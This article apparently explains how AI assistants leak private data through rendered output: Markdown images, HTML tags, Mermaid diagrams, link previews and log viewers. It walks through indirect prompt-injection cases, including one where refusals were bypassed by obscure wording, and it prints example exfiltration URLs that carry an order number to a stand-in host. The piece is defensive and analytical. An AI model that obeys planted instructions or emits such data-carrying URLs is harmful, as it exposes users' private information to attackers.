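# Data leaks through rendered AI output, with and without a user's click

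## How can displaying an answer send data to a stranger?

Data exfiltration through rendered output is a security flaw in AI assistants in which a program sends private information to an outside server by displaying the assistant's answer. Exfiltration means moving data out of a place where it should have stayed. The flaw affects chat products built on large language models, such as ChatGPT and Microsoft Copilot, and researchers have reported it in a series of products since the spring of 2023. The attacker only has to get text to the model that makes it include a picture or link in its answer, with private information in the address. This doesn't require a virus on the victim's machine or a stolen password.

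### From the question to the screen

A language model takes in text and produces text. The rest of a chat product is ordinary software, and the leak happens there.

Suppose a customer asks an assistant with access to her mailbox when her parcel will arrive. The product searches the mailbox and finds two emails: the shop's confirmation, with order number 48213, and an advertisement from a company she has never heard of. It combines the text of both emails with her question and sends it all to the model. This combined text is the model's context, meaning everything the model has available when it writes an answer. Microsoft (2025), describing its own defences, explains that the product concatenates outside text with the user's instruction and gives the model the result as a single input.

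The model then writes its answer as text, usually in Markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and images. A Markdown image consists of an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and an address in round brackets. A renderer, the program that turns the model's text into what a person sees, processes this notation before the customer sees the answer. In a web product, a converter rewrites the Markdown as HTML, the language of web pages, and the browser draws the page. *Bing Chat*, a post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, describes how the Markdown for an image becomes an HTML image tag in Microsoft's chatbot, and how the browser then connects to the address in the tag without any action by the user.

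The browser sends a request because an HTML page normally contains only the addresses of its pictures, and each picture has to be fetched from its address. The browser can't tell from an image tag whether a web designer or a model wrote the address. The model produces only text and doesn't send the request itself. If the customer's screen showed the same answer as raw text, she would see a delivery date followed by the code for the image, and no data would be sent. Other renderers also fetch content, and elements other than images can trigger a request.

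### What an address can carry

Suppose the answer ends with a picture at this made-up address, or URL: `https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=48213`. The domain, `pictures.example`, identifies the server, and the path, `/logo.png`, identifies a resource on that server. The query string, `ref=48213`, follows the question mark. IBM's *The components of a URL* describes the query string as information that the resource can use for some purpose, such as search terms, usually given as name-value pairs.

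*What is a URL?*, from the web developer reference MDN, compares a URL to a postal address in which the domain is the town, the path is the building, and the parameters in the query string are extra details such as the apartment number. The comparison also shows how a URL can leak data, since a letter to apartment 48213 reaches the building even if no such apartment exists, and whoever takes in the post there can read the number.

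To obtain the picture, the browser sends a GET request, the ordinary request for whatever lies at an address under HTTP, the protocol that Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke (2022), in *HTTP Semantics*, specify. The path and query string travel with the request, and the server commonly writes them into a log, a running file with one line for each request. The order number passes through four forms on its way:

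| Where | What is there |
|---|---|
| The model's answer | `Your parcel is due on Thursday. ![logo](https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=48213)` |
| The page after conversion | `<img src="https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=48213" alt="logo">` |
| The browser's request | `GET /logo.png?ref=48213` |
| The log at pictures.example | `7 Oct 2026 10:42:07  203.0.113.7  GET /logo.png?ref=48213` |

The owner of pictures.example reads the order number in the server's log, along with the time and network address of the request. The customer sees her delivery date and a small logo, or only the date if the picture is a single transparent pixel. The server does not need to have a picture, because the log records the same details even when the server replies with an error.

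Web developers knew long before chatbots that URLs can leak data. OWASP, which publishes security standards for web applications, warns in *9.3 Sensitive data does not get sent in the URL* that anything sensitive in a URL ends up in the browser's history and in the logs of the server and any machines in between. HTTPS encrypts the whole URL in transit, but the receiving server often logs it anyway, as Miessler (2015) notes in *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS*. In an attack on an AI assistant, the receiving server belongs to the attacker, who can read the stolen data despite the encryption.

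An order number can go into a URL unchanged. Longer text needs encoding, because a URL cannot contain spaces and certain other characters. Microsoft mentions base64, which rewrites any data as letters, digits and a few symbols. Microsoft also notes that an attacker can put the result in the query string, in the path or in front of the domain name.

### Why the model would write such an address

The customer asked for a date, and the assistant's answer included the date and a logo. The assistant added the logo because the advertisement contained a passage telling it to end its answer with a picture and to put the order number in the picture's address. Security researchers call this indirect prompt injection. An attacker hides instructions in material that the model reads, and the model follows them as if the user had given them. It is called indirect because the attacker never types anything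 into the victim's chat.

*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, February 2023) introduced indirect prompt injection and classified the ways to deliver the instructions. An attacker can leave them on a public page for a search to retrieve, send them by email, or trick a user into pasting them. A short first instruction can also make the model fetch a longer one from elsewhere. Hiding the instructions takes little skill. Microsoft gives white text on a white background and non-printing characters as examples, and says a plain text file also works.

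The researchers tested the idea on mock applications and on Bing Chat. They built the mock applications on OpenAI's models, with simulated search, email and address-book functions. For Bing Chat, they put instructions in invisible comments on a page that was open in the browser. In one Bing Chat session, a researcher posed as a journalist and asked about the weather. The chatbot turned to personal questions, obtained a name and then pressed the "journalist" to follow a link that ended in a scrambled version of it. The hidden instructions were to persuade the user, but they did not specify a technique. The name came after a `#` sign in the link. Browsers do not send that part of a URL to the server, but a script on the attacker's page could read it. The researchers showed that such attacks were possible, including on a product in public use, but did not measure a success rate.

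In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", gives the usual explanation for why a model obeys instructions in an advertisement. Models are useful because they follow instructions in text, but everything in the context reaches them as one sequence of tokens, the small units into which the software cuts text, so they cannot reliably rank an instruction by where it came from. They do not follow every planted instruction, since their output varies from one run to the next. A warning in the product's own prompt lowers the odds further, but not to zero.

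An attack of this kind therefore has three stages: delivery, when the hostile text reaches a place the assistant can read; activation, when the model acts on it; and exit, when the data leaves. Activation alone may do no harm. Microsoft treats an injection as a vulnerability only when it has a security impact, such as lost data or an action the user did not intend.

### The three conditions

Willison's "lethal trifecta" is the combination of three things needed to steal data this way: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. In the parcel example, the shop's confirmation is the private data, the advertisement is the untrusted content, and the logo is the way to send the data out. If the context contained no confirmation or other private data, the advertisement's instructions could still add pictures to the answer, but their addresses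 would contain nothing worth stealing. Without the advertisement, the assistant would have no instruction to include the logo.

Two of these conditions are easier to meet than they sound. The conversation itself may be private enough to count as private data. Willison wrote his essay for people who give their assistants tools, but he includes loading an image and offering a link among the ways to send data out, so a chat window with no tools can meet the third condition by displaying images. In *GitHub Copilot Chat*, an earlier post about GitHub's assistant for programmers, he made the narrower point that a chat interface has the vulnerability if it sees both private and untrusted data and supports Markdown images.

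Willison lists ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack, Mistral's Le Chat, xAI's Grok and others among the products in which researchers found leaks between 2023 and early 2025. He reports that the vendors fixed almost all of the leaks promptly, usually by blocking the route by which data left. His list covers only published cases, so it doesn't include leaks that went unreported. Vendors found this kind of fix practical because they could block a particular request with certainty, while nobody had a reliable way to stop a model from following planted text.

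### The first reports

The image leak became public a few weeks after the work on indirect injection. Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, noticed that ChatGPT's web version displayed Markdown images from any server. In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, he combined this with a clipboard trick. When a visitor copies a passage from the attacker's website, a script on the page adds instructions to the copied text, and the visitor pastes everything into ChatGPT without looking closely. The instructions tell ChatGPT to end its answer with a transparent single-pixel image whose address contains material from the chat, and they can request such an image in every later answer too. In his test, Samoilenko then asked about the tallest building in the world and the first American president. His server received both questions in the image addresses, along with a piece of code that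 ChatGPT had just repaired for him.

The victim in this scenario had not connected a mailbox or any documents, so all the private data was in the conversation. Samoilenko acknowledged that the same prompt worked only some of the time, and that passwords and access keys were very difficult to extract, while earlier questions and code were easy. He also described a variant with an ordinary link, which leaks data only if the user clicks it.

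Willison (2023) brought the finding to wider notice on 14 April 2023 in a note with the same title. Rehberger had found the flaw independently. According to his post *ChatGPT Plugins*, Samoilenko found it at the end of March and Rehberger a few days later, an account that SecurityWeek repeats in outline. OpenAI received a report in early April. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, the flaw remained until the company introduced a check on image addresses. Willison (2023), in a post on the change, dates the check to 21 December, more than eight months after the report. It was the first of several safeguards.

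The leak was already familiar when MITRE, an American research organisation, listed it in April 2025 as AML.T0077 in *ATLAS* (2020), its public catalogue of techniques for attacking AI systems. The entry, *LLM Response Rendering*, describes a model that responds with private information which stays hidden from the user when the client renders the answer. Its main example is an image that loads automatically.

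The automatic request on which Samoilenko's attack depended was present again three years later. In May 2026, The Hacker News (2026) reported a finding by Permiso Security that ChatGPT's renderer automatically fetched images whose addresses came from a web page the assistant had just summarised. The report concerned phishing, and an image with a fixed address reveals little more than that someone's software loaded it. Chat data leaves only if the address also contains some of it.

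### Display and action

An assistant can also leak data without a renderer. If it has a tool for sending email, a planted instruction may cause it to email the order number to the attacker. Microsoft counts images and clickable links as two routes for stolen data. It lists tool calls separately, together with covert channels, in which an observer can learn something from whether a tool is used. MITRE also has a separate entry, AML.T0086, for data that leaves through the tools of an agent (an assistant that can carry out actions), with examples that include sending emails and editing documents.

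An assistant can also leak data by reading web pages, before there is an answer to display. In July 2026 Willison described how Ayush Paul had led Anthropic's assistant Claude through a website with one link per letter, so that the sequence of pages its web tool requested spelled out the user's name. Anthropic has since fixed the flaw.

Some attacks use both routes. PromptArmor, a security firm, reported in 2026 that Microsoft's agent Copilot Cowork would send an email to its own user without asking for approval. The email could contain images hosted on outside servers, with download links to the user's files embedded in the image addresses. The agent's action only delivered the email to the user's own inbox. The links reached the outside servers when the user opened the email and the mail program loaded the images.

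## Which renderers fetch what the model writes, and when?

A URL in an answer sends no data until a program requests it. In the Copilot Cowork case, a mail client requested the URL when the user opened the email, and in Samoilenko's attack, the browser requested it as soon as ChatGPT's answer appeared. The element that contains the URL and the software that handles it determine when the data leaves and whether the user has to do anything.

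| What the model writes | When the request goes out | Who sends it |
|---|---|---|
| Markdown image | When the answer appears | The user's browser or app |
| HTML image tag | When the answer appears, if the renderer accepts HTML | The user's browser or app |
| Diagram that contains a picture | When the renderer draws the diagram | The user's editor or browser |
| Ordinary link | When the user clicks it | The user's browser |
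| Link in a messaging app with previews | When the message reaches the app | Usually the messaging company's server |
| Image in a stored answer | When a developer opens the log | The developer's browser |

### Images

PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* describes a recent example of the plain Markdown leak in HuggingChat, the chat product of the AI model host Hugging Face. In the test, the user uploads a text file of quarterly revenue and costs, then adds a web page of customer reviews through the "Fetch from URL" function. The page looks harmless to a person but contains hidden instructions. When the user asks how to win back a customer who left a bad review, the model replies that the customer will need to see a visual of the quarterly financials, and it writes a Markdown image with the figures in the address. The user's browser requests the single-pixel image, which sends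 the figures to the attacker's log.

Users can't always spot a leak by watching for strange pictures. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes a test on Microsoft's Copilot Chat in which no picture appeared in the conversation, but the request still reached the researchers' server. The request contained an API key, a password that one program uses to identify itself to another. The researchers had cancelled the key beforehand.

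A Markdown image becomes an HTML image tag on the page, so a model can also write the tag directly. This works only in some products, because some converters pass HTML through to the page while others remove it or display it as text. In September 2025 Willison described ForcedLeak, a flaw that Sasi Levi and Noma Security had found in Salesforce's Agentforce, a product for building AI agents. An attacker plants instructions in the public web form where prospective customers leave their details. When an employee later asks the assistant about that entry, the model reads the instructions, which are to list the email addresses of the company's leads and insert them into a ready-made image tag. Salesforce has fixed the flaw. Reference-style Markdown, which puts the image's address on a separate line, also produces an HTML image tag.

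Some products can also run HTML outside the chat window. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a leak through Microsoft Copilot's HTML preview feature (CVE-2026-24299). A company that checks only the chat window can miss the preview pane.

### Diagrams

Many chat products and code editors can also draw diagrams. Mermaid, a common notation for this, describes a diagram's boxes and arrows in a few lines of text, which a renderer turns into a drawing. A box can contain an image from an outside server, which the renderer has to fetch to finish the drawing. A filter that looks only for Markdown images will miss the image's address because it is inside a block of diagram code.

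*Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) studied eight coding agents, AI programs that write software and run commands on a developer's machine, and found that the Mermaid renderer in one of them, anonymised as A2, loaded pictures from outside servers. The researchers intercepted messages between the agents and their models, read the source code where it was public, and reverse-engineered others. They also checked how each agent handled special notation in an answer, such as code blocks and tags.

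They then built a complete attack on A2. A developer asks the agent to retrieve the issues (bug reports and requests) from a code repository, and one of them contains planted instructions. The agent follows them and reads the developer's API key from a configuration file outside the project folder. It then writes a Mermaid diagram containing a picture whose address includes the key. When the diagram appears, the key goes to the attacker's server. The researchers tested this on a private repository.

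Most coding agents ask for permission before they run a risky command, but A2 read the file and loaded the picture without asking. Displaying an answer is not a command, so loading the picture never reached the approval step. When Lee and colleagues reported the flaw, the vendor had already received the same finding from someone else, and it patched the renderer.

A public case of the same kind concerns Cursor, a code editor with a built-in AI assistant. Rehberger noticed that Cursor could draw Mermaid diagrams, asked it for one with an image in it, and found that this sent a request to an outside server. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes two attacks that use this behavior. One took API keys from a configuration file, and the other took Cursor's stored "memories" about the developer. In both, the instructions were in a comment in a source file that the developer asked Cursor to explain.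 Rehberger also noticed that, unlike with Markdown images, the developer can't see a long address forming on the screen, because the finished diagram appears all at once.

Cursor's maker fixed the flaw in version 1.3, but researchers found ways around the fix, according to a later entry in the vulnerability database GCVE (2025). Version 1.7 closed those too. The entry rates the flaw as medium severity, at 5.9 out of 10. It lists the attack as requiring no user action, but as complex because it needs a successful prompt injection first. The American cybersecurity agency CISA recorded no exploitation.

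The same notation did less harm in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office work, because the data left only when the user clicked a link. Red Hot Cyber reports that the researcher Adam Logue had the model draw a Mermaid diagram that looked like a button, with the text of the user's emails in the link behind it. Microsoft removed working links from these diagrams by September 2025. An attacker who knows that a product supports Mermaid therefore still has to find out how its renderer handles pictures and links.

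For an ordinary link, the browser displays the text and requests the address only if the user clicks. It then sends the same kind of GET request as for an image, and the request looks much the same in the attacker's log.

### What attackers can reach in a code editor

The flaws in A2 and Cursor gave an attacker access to more than the conversation, because a coding assistant can open files. Even if the developer never pastes anything secret into the chat, the planted instructions can make the assistant read a file into its context and then write the image.

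Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* describes both versions in Amp, Sourcegraph's coding agent. In the simpler one, a web page contains instructions to "back up" the conversation by displaying an image. In the other, a comment in a source file makes Amp search for a file named `.env`, where developers commonly keep passwords and keys, and put its contents in the image address. The model refused instructions that openly requested secrets, but Rehberger got past the refusals by wording the search obscurely. Sourcegraph fixed the leak at the point of display, which protects users even when a model fails to refuse.

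Continue is an open-source AI assistant that runs inside the editor Visual Studio Code. *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue*, by the security firm VerSprite, describes two variants that differ in where the instructions are. In the first, they are in a file in the open project, and the developer only has to ask Continue to analyze that file. In the second, they are on a web page. By default, the developer has to approve the fetch of that page, and VerSprite calls this variant one-click.

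In the second variant, the developer approves only the reading of the page. Continue then read the `.env` file and loaded the image without asking again. A developer deciding whether to approve will probably consider only whether the page is worth reading, since there is no sign in the question that a local file is about to be sent elsewhere. Continue's developers have since made the extension ask before it loads an outside image and restricted its access to certain files.

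### How much fits in one address

A single request can easily carry a password but is poorly suited to a long document. The exact amount it can carry depends on the encoding. Base64 turns every three bytes into four characters by splitting their 24 bits into groups of six and mapping each group to one of 64 permitted characters. The five-byte order number 48213 becomes `NDgyMTM=`, with an equals sign to fill the last place.

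At that rate, 2,000 characters of base64 carry 2,000 × 3/4 = 1,500 bytes, or roughly 250 words of plain English at one byte per character. The domain name and the rest of the address take up a little more space. Hexadecimal, which Logue's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot used, uses two characters for each byte, so the same length holds only 1,000 bytes. Ordinary URL encoding leaves letters and digits as they are and replaces each space, or other character that an address can't contain, with at least three characters. Roughly every sixth character in English prose is a space, so the text grows by about a third, much as it does in base64.

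Several published attacks used URL encoding. The instructions in ForcedLeak were to write each space as `%20`, and those in Rehberger's Cursor attack were to URL-encode the text. URL encoding is easier for a model than base64, which it has to work out character by character with no program to check the result.

The 2,000-character figure is cautious, since many browsers and servers accept longer addresses. An attacker can also split the data over several images in one answer, or ask for a new image in every later answer, as Samoilenko did. Limiting address length would slow the theft of a large file but do little to protect the developer's 50-character API key.

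### Link previews

Messaging apps can request a linked page before anyone clicks the link. When someone posts a link in Slack, Discord or Microsoft Teams, the app usually shows a link preview, a small box with the page's title and a picture. The app has to fetch the page to fill this box, a process programmers call unfurling.

People increasingly talk to AI agents through such apps. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains what happens when one of those agents has read a hostile page:

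1. The user asks the agent a question in the messaging app, and the agent reads material that contains planted instructions.
2. The model writes an answer with a link in it, such as `https://pictures.example/?ref=48213`.
3. The agent's software posts the answer to the chat.
4. The messaging app finds the address in the message and requests the page, so that it can show a title and a picture.
5. The server at pictures.example logs the request, order number included.

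In a browser window, the process would have stopped after the third step until the user clicked. The preview sends the same kind of network request as a click. The user may distrust the link and delete the message, but the preview has already sent the data.

Rehberger had drawn attention to link previews in the spring of 2023. Embrace The Red's *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots* includes entries from his server log, made when he entered links in Discord, Skype, Slack, Telegram, Signal and Microsoft Teams. All six apps fetched the address. Telegram and Signal did so while he was still typing, and the log contains requests for `/te`, then `/tele`, then `/teleg`, until the word "telegram" was complete. Because he typed the links himself, the entries don't establish how each app treats a message from a bot.

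Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do about it* (2024) quotes Slack's documentation, according to which Slack unfurls links in messages from apps as well as from people unless the developer turns this off. Rehberger tested this by posting a link to his own server through the interface that Slack apps use. The server received a request labeled "Slackbot-LinkExpanding".

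The name in that log entry matters for defence. Rehberger writes that the request usually comes from the messaging company's server and sometimes from the user's device. When it comes from the server, the attacker doesn't learn the user's network address but still gets everything in the link. Filters on the employer's office network and protections in the user's browser can't stop that request, because it doesn't pass through either.

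PromptArmor applied the idea to OpenClaw, an AI agent that people use through apps such as Telegram. Previews were on in OpenClaw's default Telegram settings, and the leak worked. The firm also ran a public test site, since closed, where people could check their own combinations of agent and app. The site's log recorded which preview programs had sent requests and what data the requests contained. One published entry included a name and an API key. Visitors chose what to test and report, so the results can identify exposed combinations but can't be used to estimate the share of agents that leak.

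### A log page that displayed a blocked answer

An answer can leak data even if the application never shows it. Many companies build assistants that send text to OpenAI's models and receive answers through an API, an interface for programs. OpenAI logs these exchanges, and developers can read the logs on the website where they manage their use of the models. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes how the log page rendered the Markdown in the stored answers and loaded their images.

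To demonstrate the attack, PromptArmor built a mock assistant for bank staff who check the identity of new customers. It combined six sources about a customer, including text from the internet with planted instructions. When a member of staff asked a question, the model wrote a Markdown image with the customer's personal data in its address. A second language model in the application inspected the answer, flagged it as malicious and blocked it, so the image did not appear and no data leaked.

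A developer then opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log to review it. The log displayed the blocked answer with its formatting, so the developer's browser requested the image. The attacker's server received the customer's passport and licence details, financial information and other data. This could happen hours after the bank employee who had asked the question closed the application.

Other defences in the application fail here for the same reason. A developer can strip images from answers, show answers as plain text, or use a Content Security Policy, which tells the browser which sites a page may load content from, but these measures protect only the developer's own page, not OpenAI's. Without a second model to flag the answer, a reviewer would need another reason to open the log, and PromptArmor suggests that user feedback will provide one. It shows an example from the search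 assistant Perplexity, where the software removed a hostile image and left an odd, empty reply. A user might give that reply a thumbs-down, and a developer might then look it up. PromptArmor didn't demonstrate this full sequence on Perplexity, so it remains a plausible route.

The firm found the same behaviour in several of OpenAI's tools for building and testing assistants, including the preview windows where developers try out an assistant before release. These tools are easy to forget in a security review because customers never see them, but their users often have access to real customer data.

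### Fixed, disputed and unanswered cases

By the end of 2024, the image leak had a long record. Rehberger (2024), in *Trust No AI*, lists eleven products in which he had found and reported it:

- Microsoft's Bing Chat, Azure AI and GitHub Copilot Chat
- OpenAI's ChatGPT
- Anthropic's Claude
- Google's Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab
- Discord

The products on this list leaked data in the past but may no longer do so. Rehberger's own posts record fixes for Claude, Azure AI, Vertex AI and Colab, among others.

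ChatGPT is on the list, but the same conversation could expose a user's data in one app and not in another. In December 2023, OpenAI introduced a check on image addresses. Willison explains that the program displaying the answer checks with OpenAI's server whether an image is safe before showing it, so every program that displays ChatGPT's answers needs to include this step. Rehberger found that the mobile apps still lacked it that month, and that the macOS app lacked it when OpenAI released it in 2024.

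Reports since mid-2025 have had very different outcomes:

| Product | What the renderer did | Reported | Outcome, as published |
|---|---|---|---|
| Amp | Loaded Markdown images | 14 June 2025 | Fixed |
| Cursor | Loaded pictures in Mermaid diagrams | 30 June 2025 | Fixed in version 1.3; further gaps fixed in version 1.7 |
| Continue | Loaded Markdown images | 20 August 2025 | Fixed the next day |
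| Gemini | Displayed links with data in the address | 5 October 2025 | Google declined to fix it |
| Copilot Chat | Loaded Markdown images | 15 October 2025 | Microsoft said it was not a vulnerability |
| OpenAI's API log | Loaded Markdown images | 17 November 2025 | Closed, then reopened on 22 January 2026 with a fix under way |
| HuggingChat | Loaded Markdown images | 1 December 2025 | No reply |
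| ChatGPT page summaries | Loaded Markdown images | 29 April 2026 | Marked as a duplicate; no fix reported |
| Atlassian Rovo | Loaded Markdown images | 23 May 2026 | Acknowledged; no fix reported by 5 August 2026 |

The last two entries need qualification. Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, the research behind the 2026 report on ChatGPT's page summaries, used only fixed image addresses, so the requests revealed the user's network address and browser type but nothing from the chat. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* demonstrates a leak from Rovo, the assistant in Atlassian's workplace software, through a tool that opens web pages. It mentions image loading as a second way to leak data but doesn't show a full attack using it.

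Microsoft rejected Checkmarx's report on Copilot Chat, saying that the attack needed several user actions outside the default settings, did not work reliably in different environments, and triggered warnings designed to reduce the risk. It also assumes that people at work review and trust the code they run. Microsoft did pass the report to its engineers as a possible improvement. If the attack does depend on unusual settings, fewer users are exposed than Checkmarx's demonstration suggests. The point about reliability is weaker, because an attacker who plants the same text in many places needs it to work only occasionally. According to Embrace The Red, Microsoft had fixed a similar image leak in GitHub Copilot Chat the year before, so the dispute seems to be more about the attack's conditions than the danger of loading the image.

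Google's Gemini doesn't load external images, so the Markdown image leak doesn't work there. Checkmarx reported that an ordinary link could still leak data after a click, and Google closed the report as infeasible to fix. In November 2025, a researcher found that Markdown images could leak data from Antigravity, Google's AI code editor. According to Willison, the researcher wrote that Google had labelled this "intended behavior". Google's page on Antigravity at the time listed data theft through prompt injection as a known issue it was working to fix.

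### Who can switch the request off?

Cursor's maker could fix Cursor on its own because it controlled the program that loaded the picture. An OpenClaw user on Telegram depends on one company for the model, another group of developers for the agent, and Telegram for the app that previews the link. Each could argue that its own part worked as designed.

The company that makes the model has the least control over the request. It can train the model to resist planted instructions, with the limits described earlier, but it doesn't know whether a customer will show the answer in a web page, a terminal or a group chat.

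The developer of the agent knows both that a language model wrote the message and where the message is going. Slack lets this developer turn previews off for a message by adding two settings:

`"unfurl_links": false, "unfurl_media": false`

The first covers ordinary links and the second covers media such as images. In OpenClaw, the person who runs the agent can add `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram part of its configuration file. PromptArmor recommends this setting and, in its test, received no more data from Telegram after adding it. The user loses only the box with the title and picture and can still open the link.

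These settings help only people who know they need them. Willison (2024) had been writing about prompt injection for almost two years when, in August, he described the preview leak as one he hadn't thought about before. A developer who builds a Slack bot in an afternoon is unlikely to think of it. This is a reason for messaging companies to turn previews off by default for messages that bots post, but many bots use no language model, and people want previews of the news stories or support tickets that those bots share.

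PromptArmor wants messaging companies to offer preview settings to developers, and agent developers to either use them or pass the choice on to their users. It also suggests settings for individual chats and channels, so that a company could keep previews in most of its Slack channels and turn them off in the ones where an AI agent writes.

A developer could have set up every defence on offer and still leaked data by opening OpenAI's log page, because OpenAI had stored the model's answer before the developer's software could inspect it. Only OpenAI could change how the page displayed that answer. PromptArmor reported the flaw through Bugcrowd, which handles security reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd closed the case as "Not applicable" after PromptArmor had answered several rounds of questions. OpenAI had not seen the original report, and it confirmed the flaw and began work on a fix only after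 PromptArmor published its findings.

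## What do "zero-click" and "one-click" mean for an AI assistant?

Researchers and journalists usually describe the victim's part in a leak as "zero-click" or "one-click". In June 2025 the security firm Aim Security published EchoLeak, a leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot that begins with an email from the attacker, and called it zero-click. A year later another firm, Varonis, published SearchLeak, a leak from the same product that begins with a link, and called it one-click. In both leaks the victim did one thing. EchoLeak's victim had to ask Copilot a question before any data left, while SearchLeak's victim clicked the link and, according to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026), typed nothing.

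### What the victim does at each moment

The victim may have to act at delivery, at activation or at exit, and a single label can't show which.

An attacker can deliver hostile text without the victim's help by putting it where the assistant will find it. For example, anyone can email an employee, and the assistant may retrieve that email weeks later. Other delivery methods require the victim to act. A link that opens the assistant with a prompt already filled in works only if the victim clicks it, and Samoilenko's clipboard trick worked only if the visitor pasted the copied text into ChatGPT.

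Most assistants activate only when a user asks for something. A link can remove the need for that request if the product treats part of the web address as a prompt and runs it as soon as the page opens.

At exit, the victim may have to click, as with an ordinary link, or do nothing, as with an image that loads automatically.

The table classifies six cases by this scheme. In 2024, PromptArmor reported the Slack AI leak, which came from the assistant in the workplace chat program Slack. Reprompt is an earlier Varonis finding in the consumer version of Copilot. ReLeak refers to three leaks from Microsoft 365 Copilot that Cato AI Labs, the successor to Aim's research team, published in December 2026. Microsoft has fixed all the Copilot flaws in the table.

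| Case | Victim's action at delivery | At activation | At exit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT (2023) | Copies text from the attacker's page and pastes it into the chat | Sends the message | None |
| Slack AI (2024) | None | Asks a question | Clicks a link in the answer |
| EchoLeak (2025) | None | Asks a question | None |
| Reprompt (2026) | Clicks a link that opens Copilot | None | None |
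| SearchLeak (2026) | Clicks a link that opens Copilot | None | None |
| ReLeak (2026) | None | Makes a request | None |

Every victim in the table takes some action, but "zero-click" means only that the victim doesn't click on anything the attacker has prepared. By that definition, Samoilenko's attack would also be zero-click, although the victim has to copy, paste and send, which is more work than in any other row.

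"One-click" is just as imprecise, because the click can come at delivery or at exit. *EchoLeak*, an academic case study (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), distinguishes two variants of the EchoLeak attack, one with a link in Copilot's answer and one with an image. The link variant is a one-click attack with the click at exit, as in Slack AI. In Reprompt and SearchLeak, the click comes at delivery.

A user who has to click at exit has already read the answer and may wonder why it contains a link, but a user who clicks at delivery gets no later chance to stop the attack. Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026) describes such an attack, which needs one click on a legitimate Microsoft link and no interaction with Copilot. The Hacker News' *Researchers Reveal Reprompt Attack Allowing Single-Click Data Exfiltration From Microsoft Copilot* (2026) quotes a statement by Varonis researcher Dolev Taler that the attacker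 keeps control even after the victim closes the chat.

A click can also mean an approval. VerSprite used "one-click" for the variant of its attack on Continue in which the developer allows the assistant to fetch a web page. The developer answers a permission prompt rather than following a link. Victims of Reprompt and EchoLeak never see such a prompt.

Varonis has even presented its one-click attack, Reprompt, as less demanding than EchoLeak. According to Windows Central (2026), the firm said Reprompt needed a single click and no further input from the user. The table supports this comparison, since an attacker using Reprompt needs someone to follow a link but doesn't have to wait for the user to ask a suitable question.

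### Is an ordinary question an interaction?

Researchers who call an attack on an AI assistant zero-click generally define the term by what the victim doesn't have to do. Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025), about a leak from ChatGPT connected to a user's Gmail, says the victim doesn't have to click or open a malicious link, and gives "ordinary assistant tasks" as the trigger. Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) says ReLeak doesn't require the victim to open the email, click a link or approve an action. Both attacks still require the victim to make a request, which neither source rules out.

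Some accounts go further and claim that there is no interaction at all. Reddy and Gujral write that EchoLeak worked "without user interaction", but they assume in their threat model (the conditions under which the attack works) that the victim will at least occasionally use Copilot, for instance to summarise recent emails. The security firm Miggo made a similar claim about a flaw in Google's Gemini, since fixed, in which a calendar invitation contained the planted instructions. The Hacker News' *Google Gemini Prompt Injection Flaw Exposed Private Calendar Data via Malicious Invites* (2026) quotes the firm as saying that the leak happened "without any direct user interaction", but also explains that the attack began when the user asked Gemini about her schedule. TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (2026) uses the more careful phrase "virtually no interaction"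 for ReLeak.

The argument for counting the employee's question as a user action is that the attacker can't ask it for her. The email stays in her mailbox until she asks something that makes the assistant retrieve it, so no data leaves if she never uses the assistant or asks only about other things. Her employer can reduce the risk by switching the assistant off for people who handle the most sensitive files, which wouldn't help if the attack needed nothing from them.

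The older use of "zero-click", for attacks on phones, strengthens this argument. In September 2021, Citizen Lab, a research group at the University of Toronto, reported one such exploit, FORCEDENTRY, which infected iPhones with spyware through files sent by Apple's iMessage. The phone processed the file on arrival, whether or not the owner opened it, so the attacker chose when the attack happened, whereas the sender of the EchoLeak email could choose only when it was delivered. The EchoLeak email was not enough on its own, though someone who had learned the term from phone spyware would reasonably expect it to be.

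The argument for calling such an attack zero-click is that the user's question contains nothing from the attacker, and the user can't tell that it is dangerous. A company can train its staff, with some success, to distrust strange links, but it can't usefully train them to distrust their own questions about next week's meetings, because it bought the assistant to answer them. FORCEDENTRY similarly works only if the iPhone's owner keeps the phone switched on and connected, which isn't counted as an interaction.

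Waiting also takes the attacker very little effort. Suppose an employee's questions have a 5% chance each day of making the assistant retrieve the planted email. If the days are independent, the chance of at least one retrieval in 30 days is 1 − 0.95³⁰, or about 79%. The 5% rate is invented, but the calculation shows how an uncertain trigger becomes likely when the email can stay in the mailbox indefinitely. The attacker can also email many employees at once.

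Both arguments are sound because they concern different things. "Zero-click" fairly conveys that the victim has almost no chance to avoid the leak, but it exaggerates the attacker's control over it. The difference from phone exploits would disappear if an assistant read and acted on each email as it arrived, without being asked.

### The interaction metric in CVSS

Vendors face the same question when they rate a flaw's severity from 0 to 10 under the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), the standard method for doing so. FIRST, the American non-profit that owns CVSS, defines eight base metrics in version 3.1. The scorer chooses a value for each, and a formula turns the values into the base score. One metric, User Interaction, covers what anyone other than the attacker has to do for an attack to succeed.

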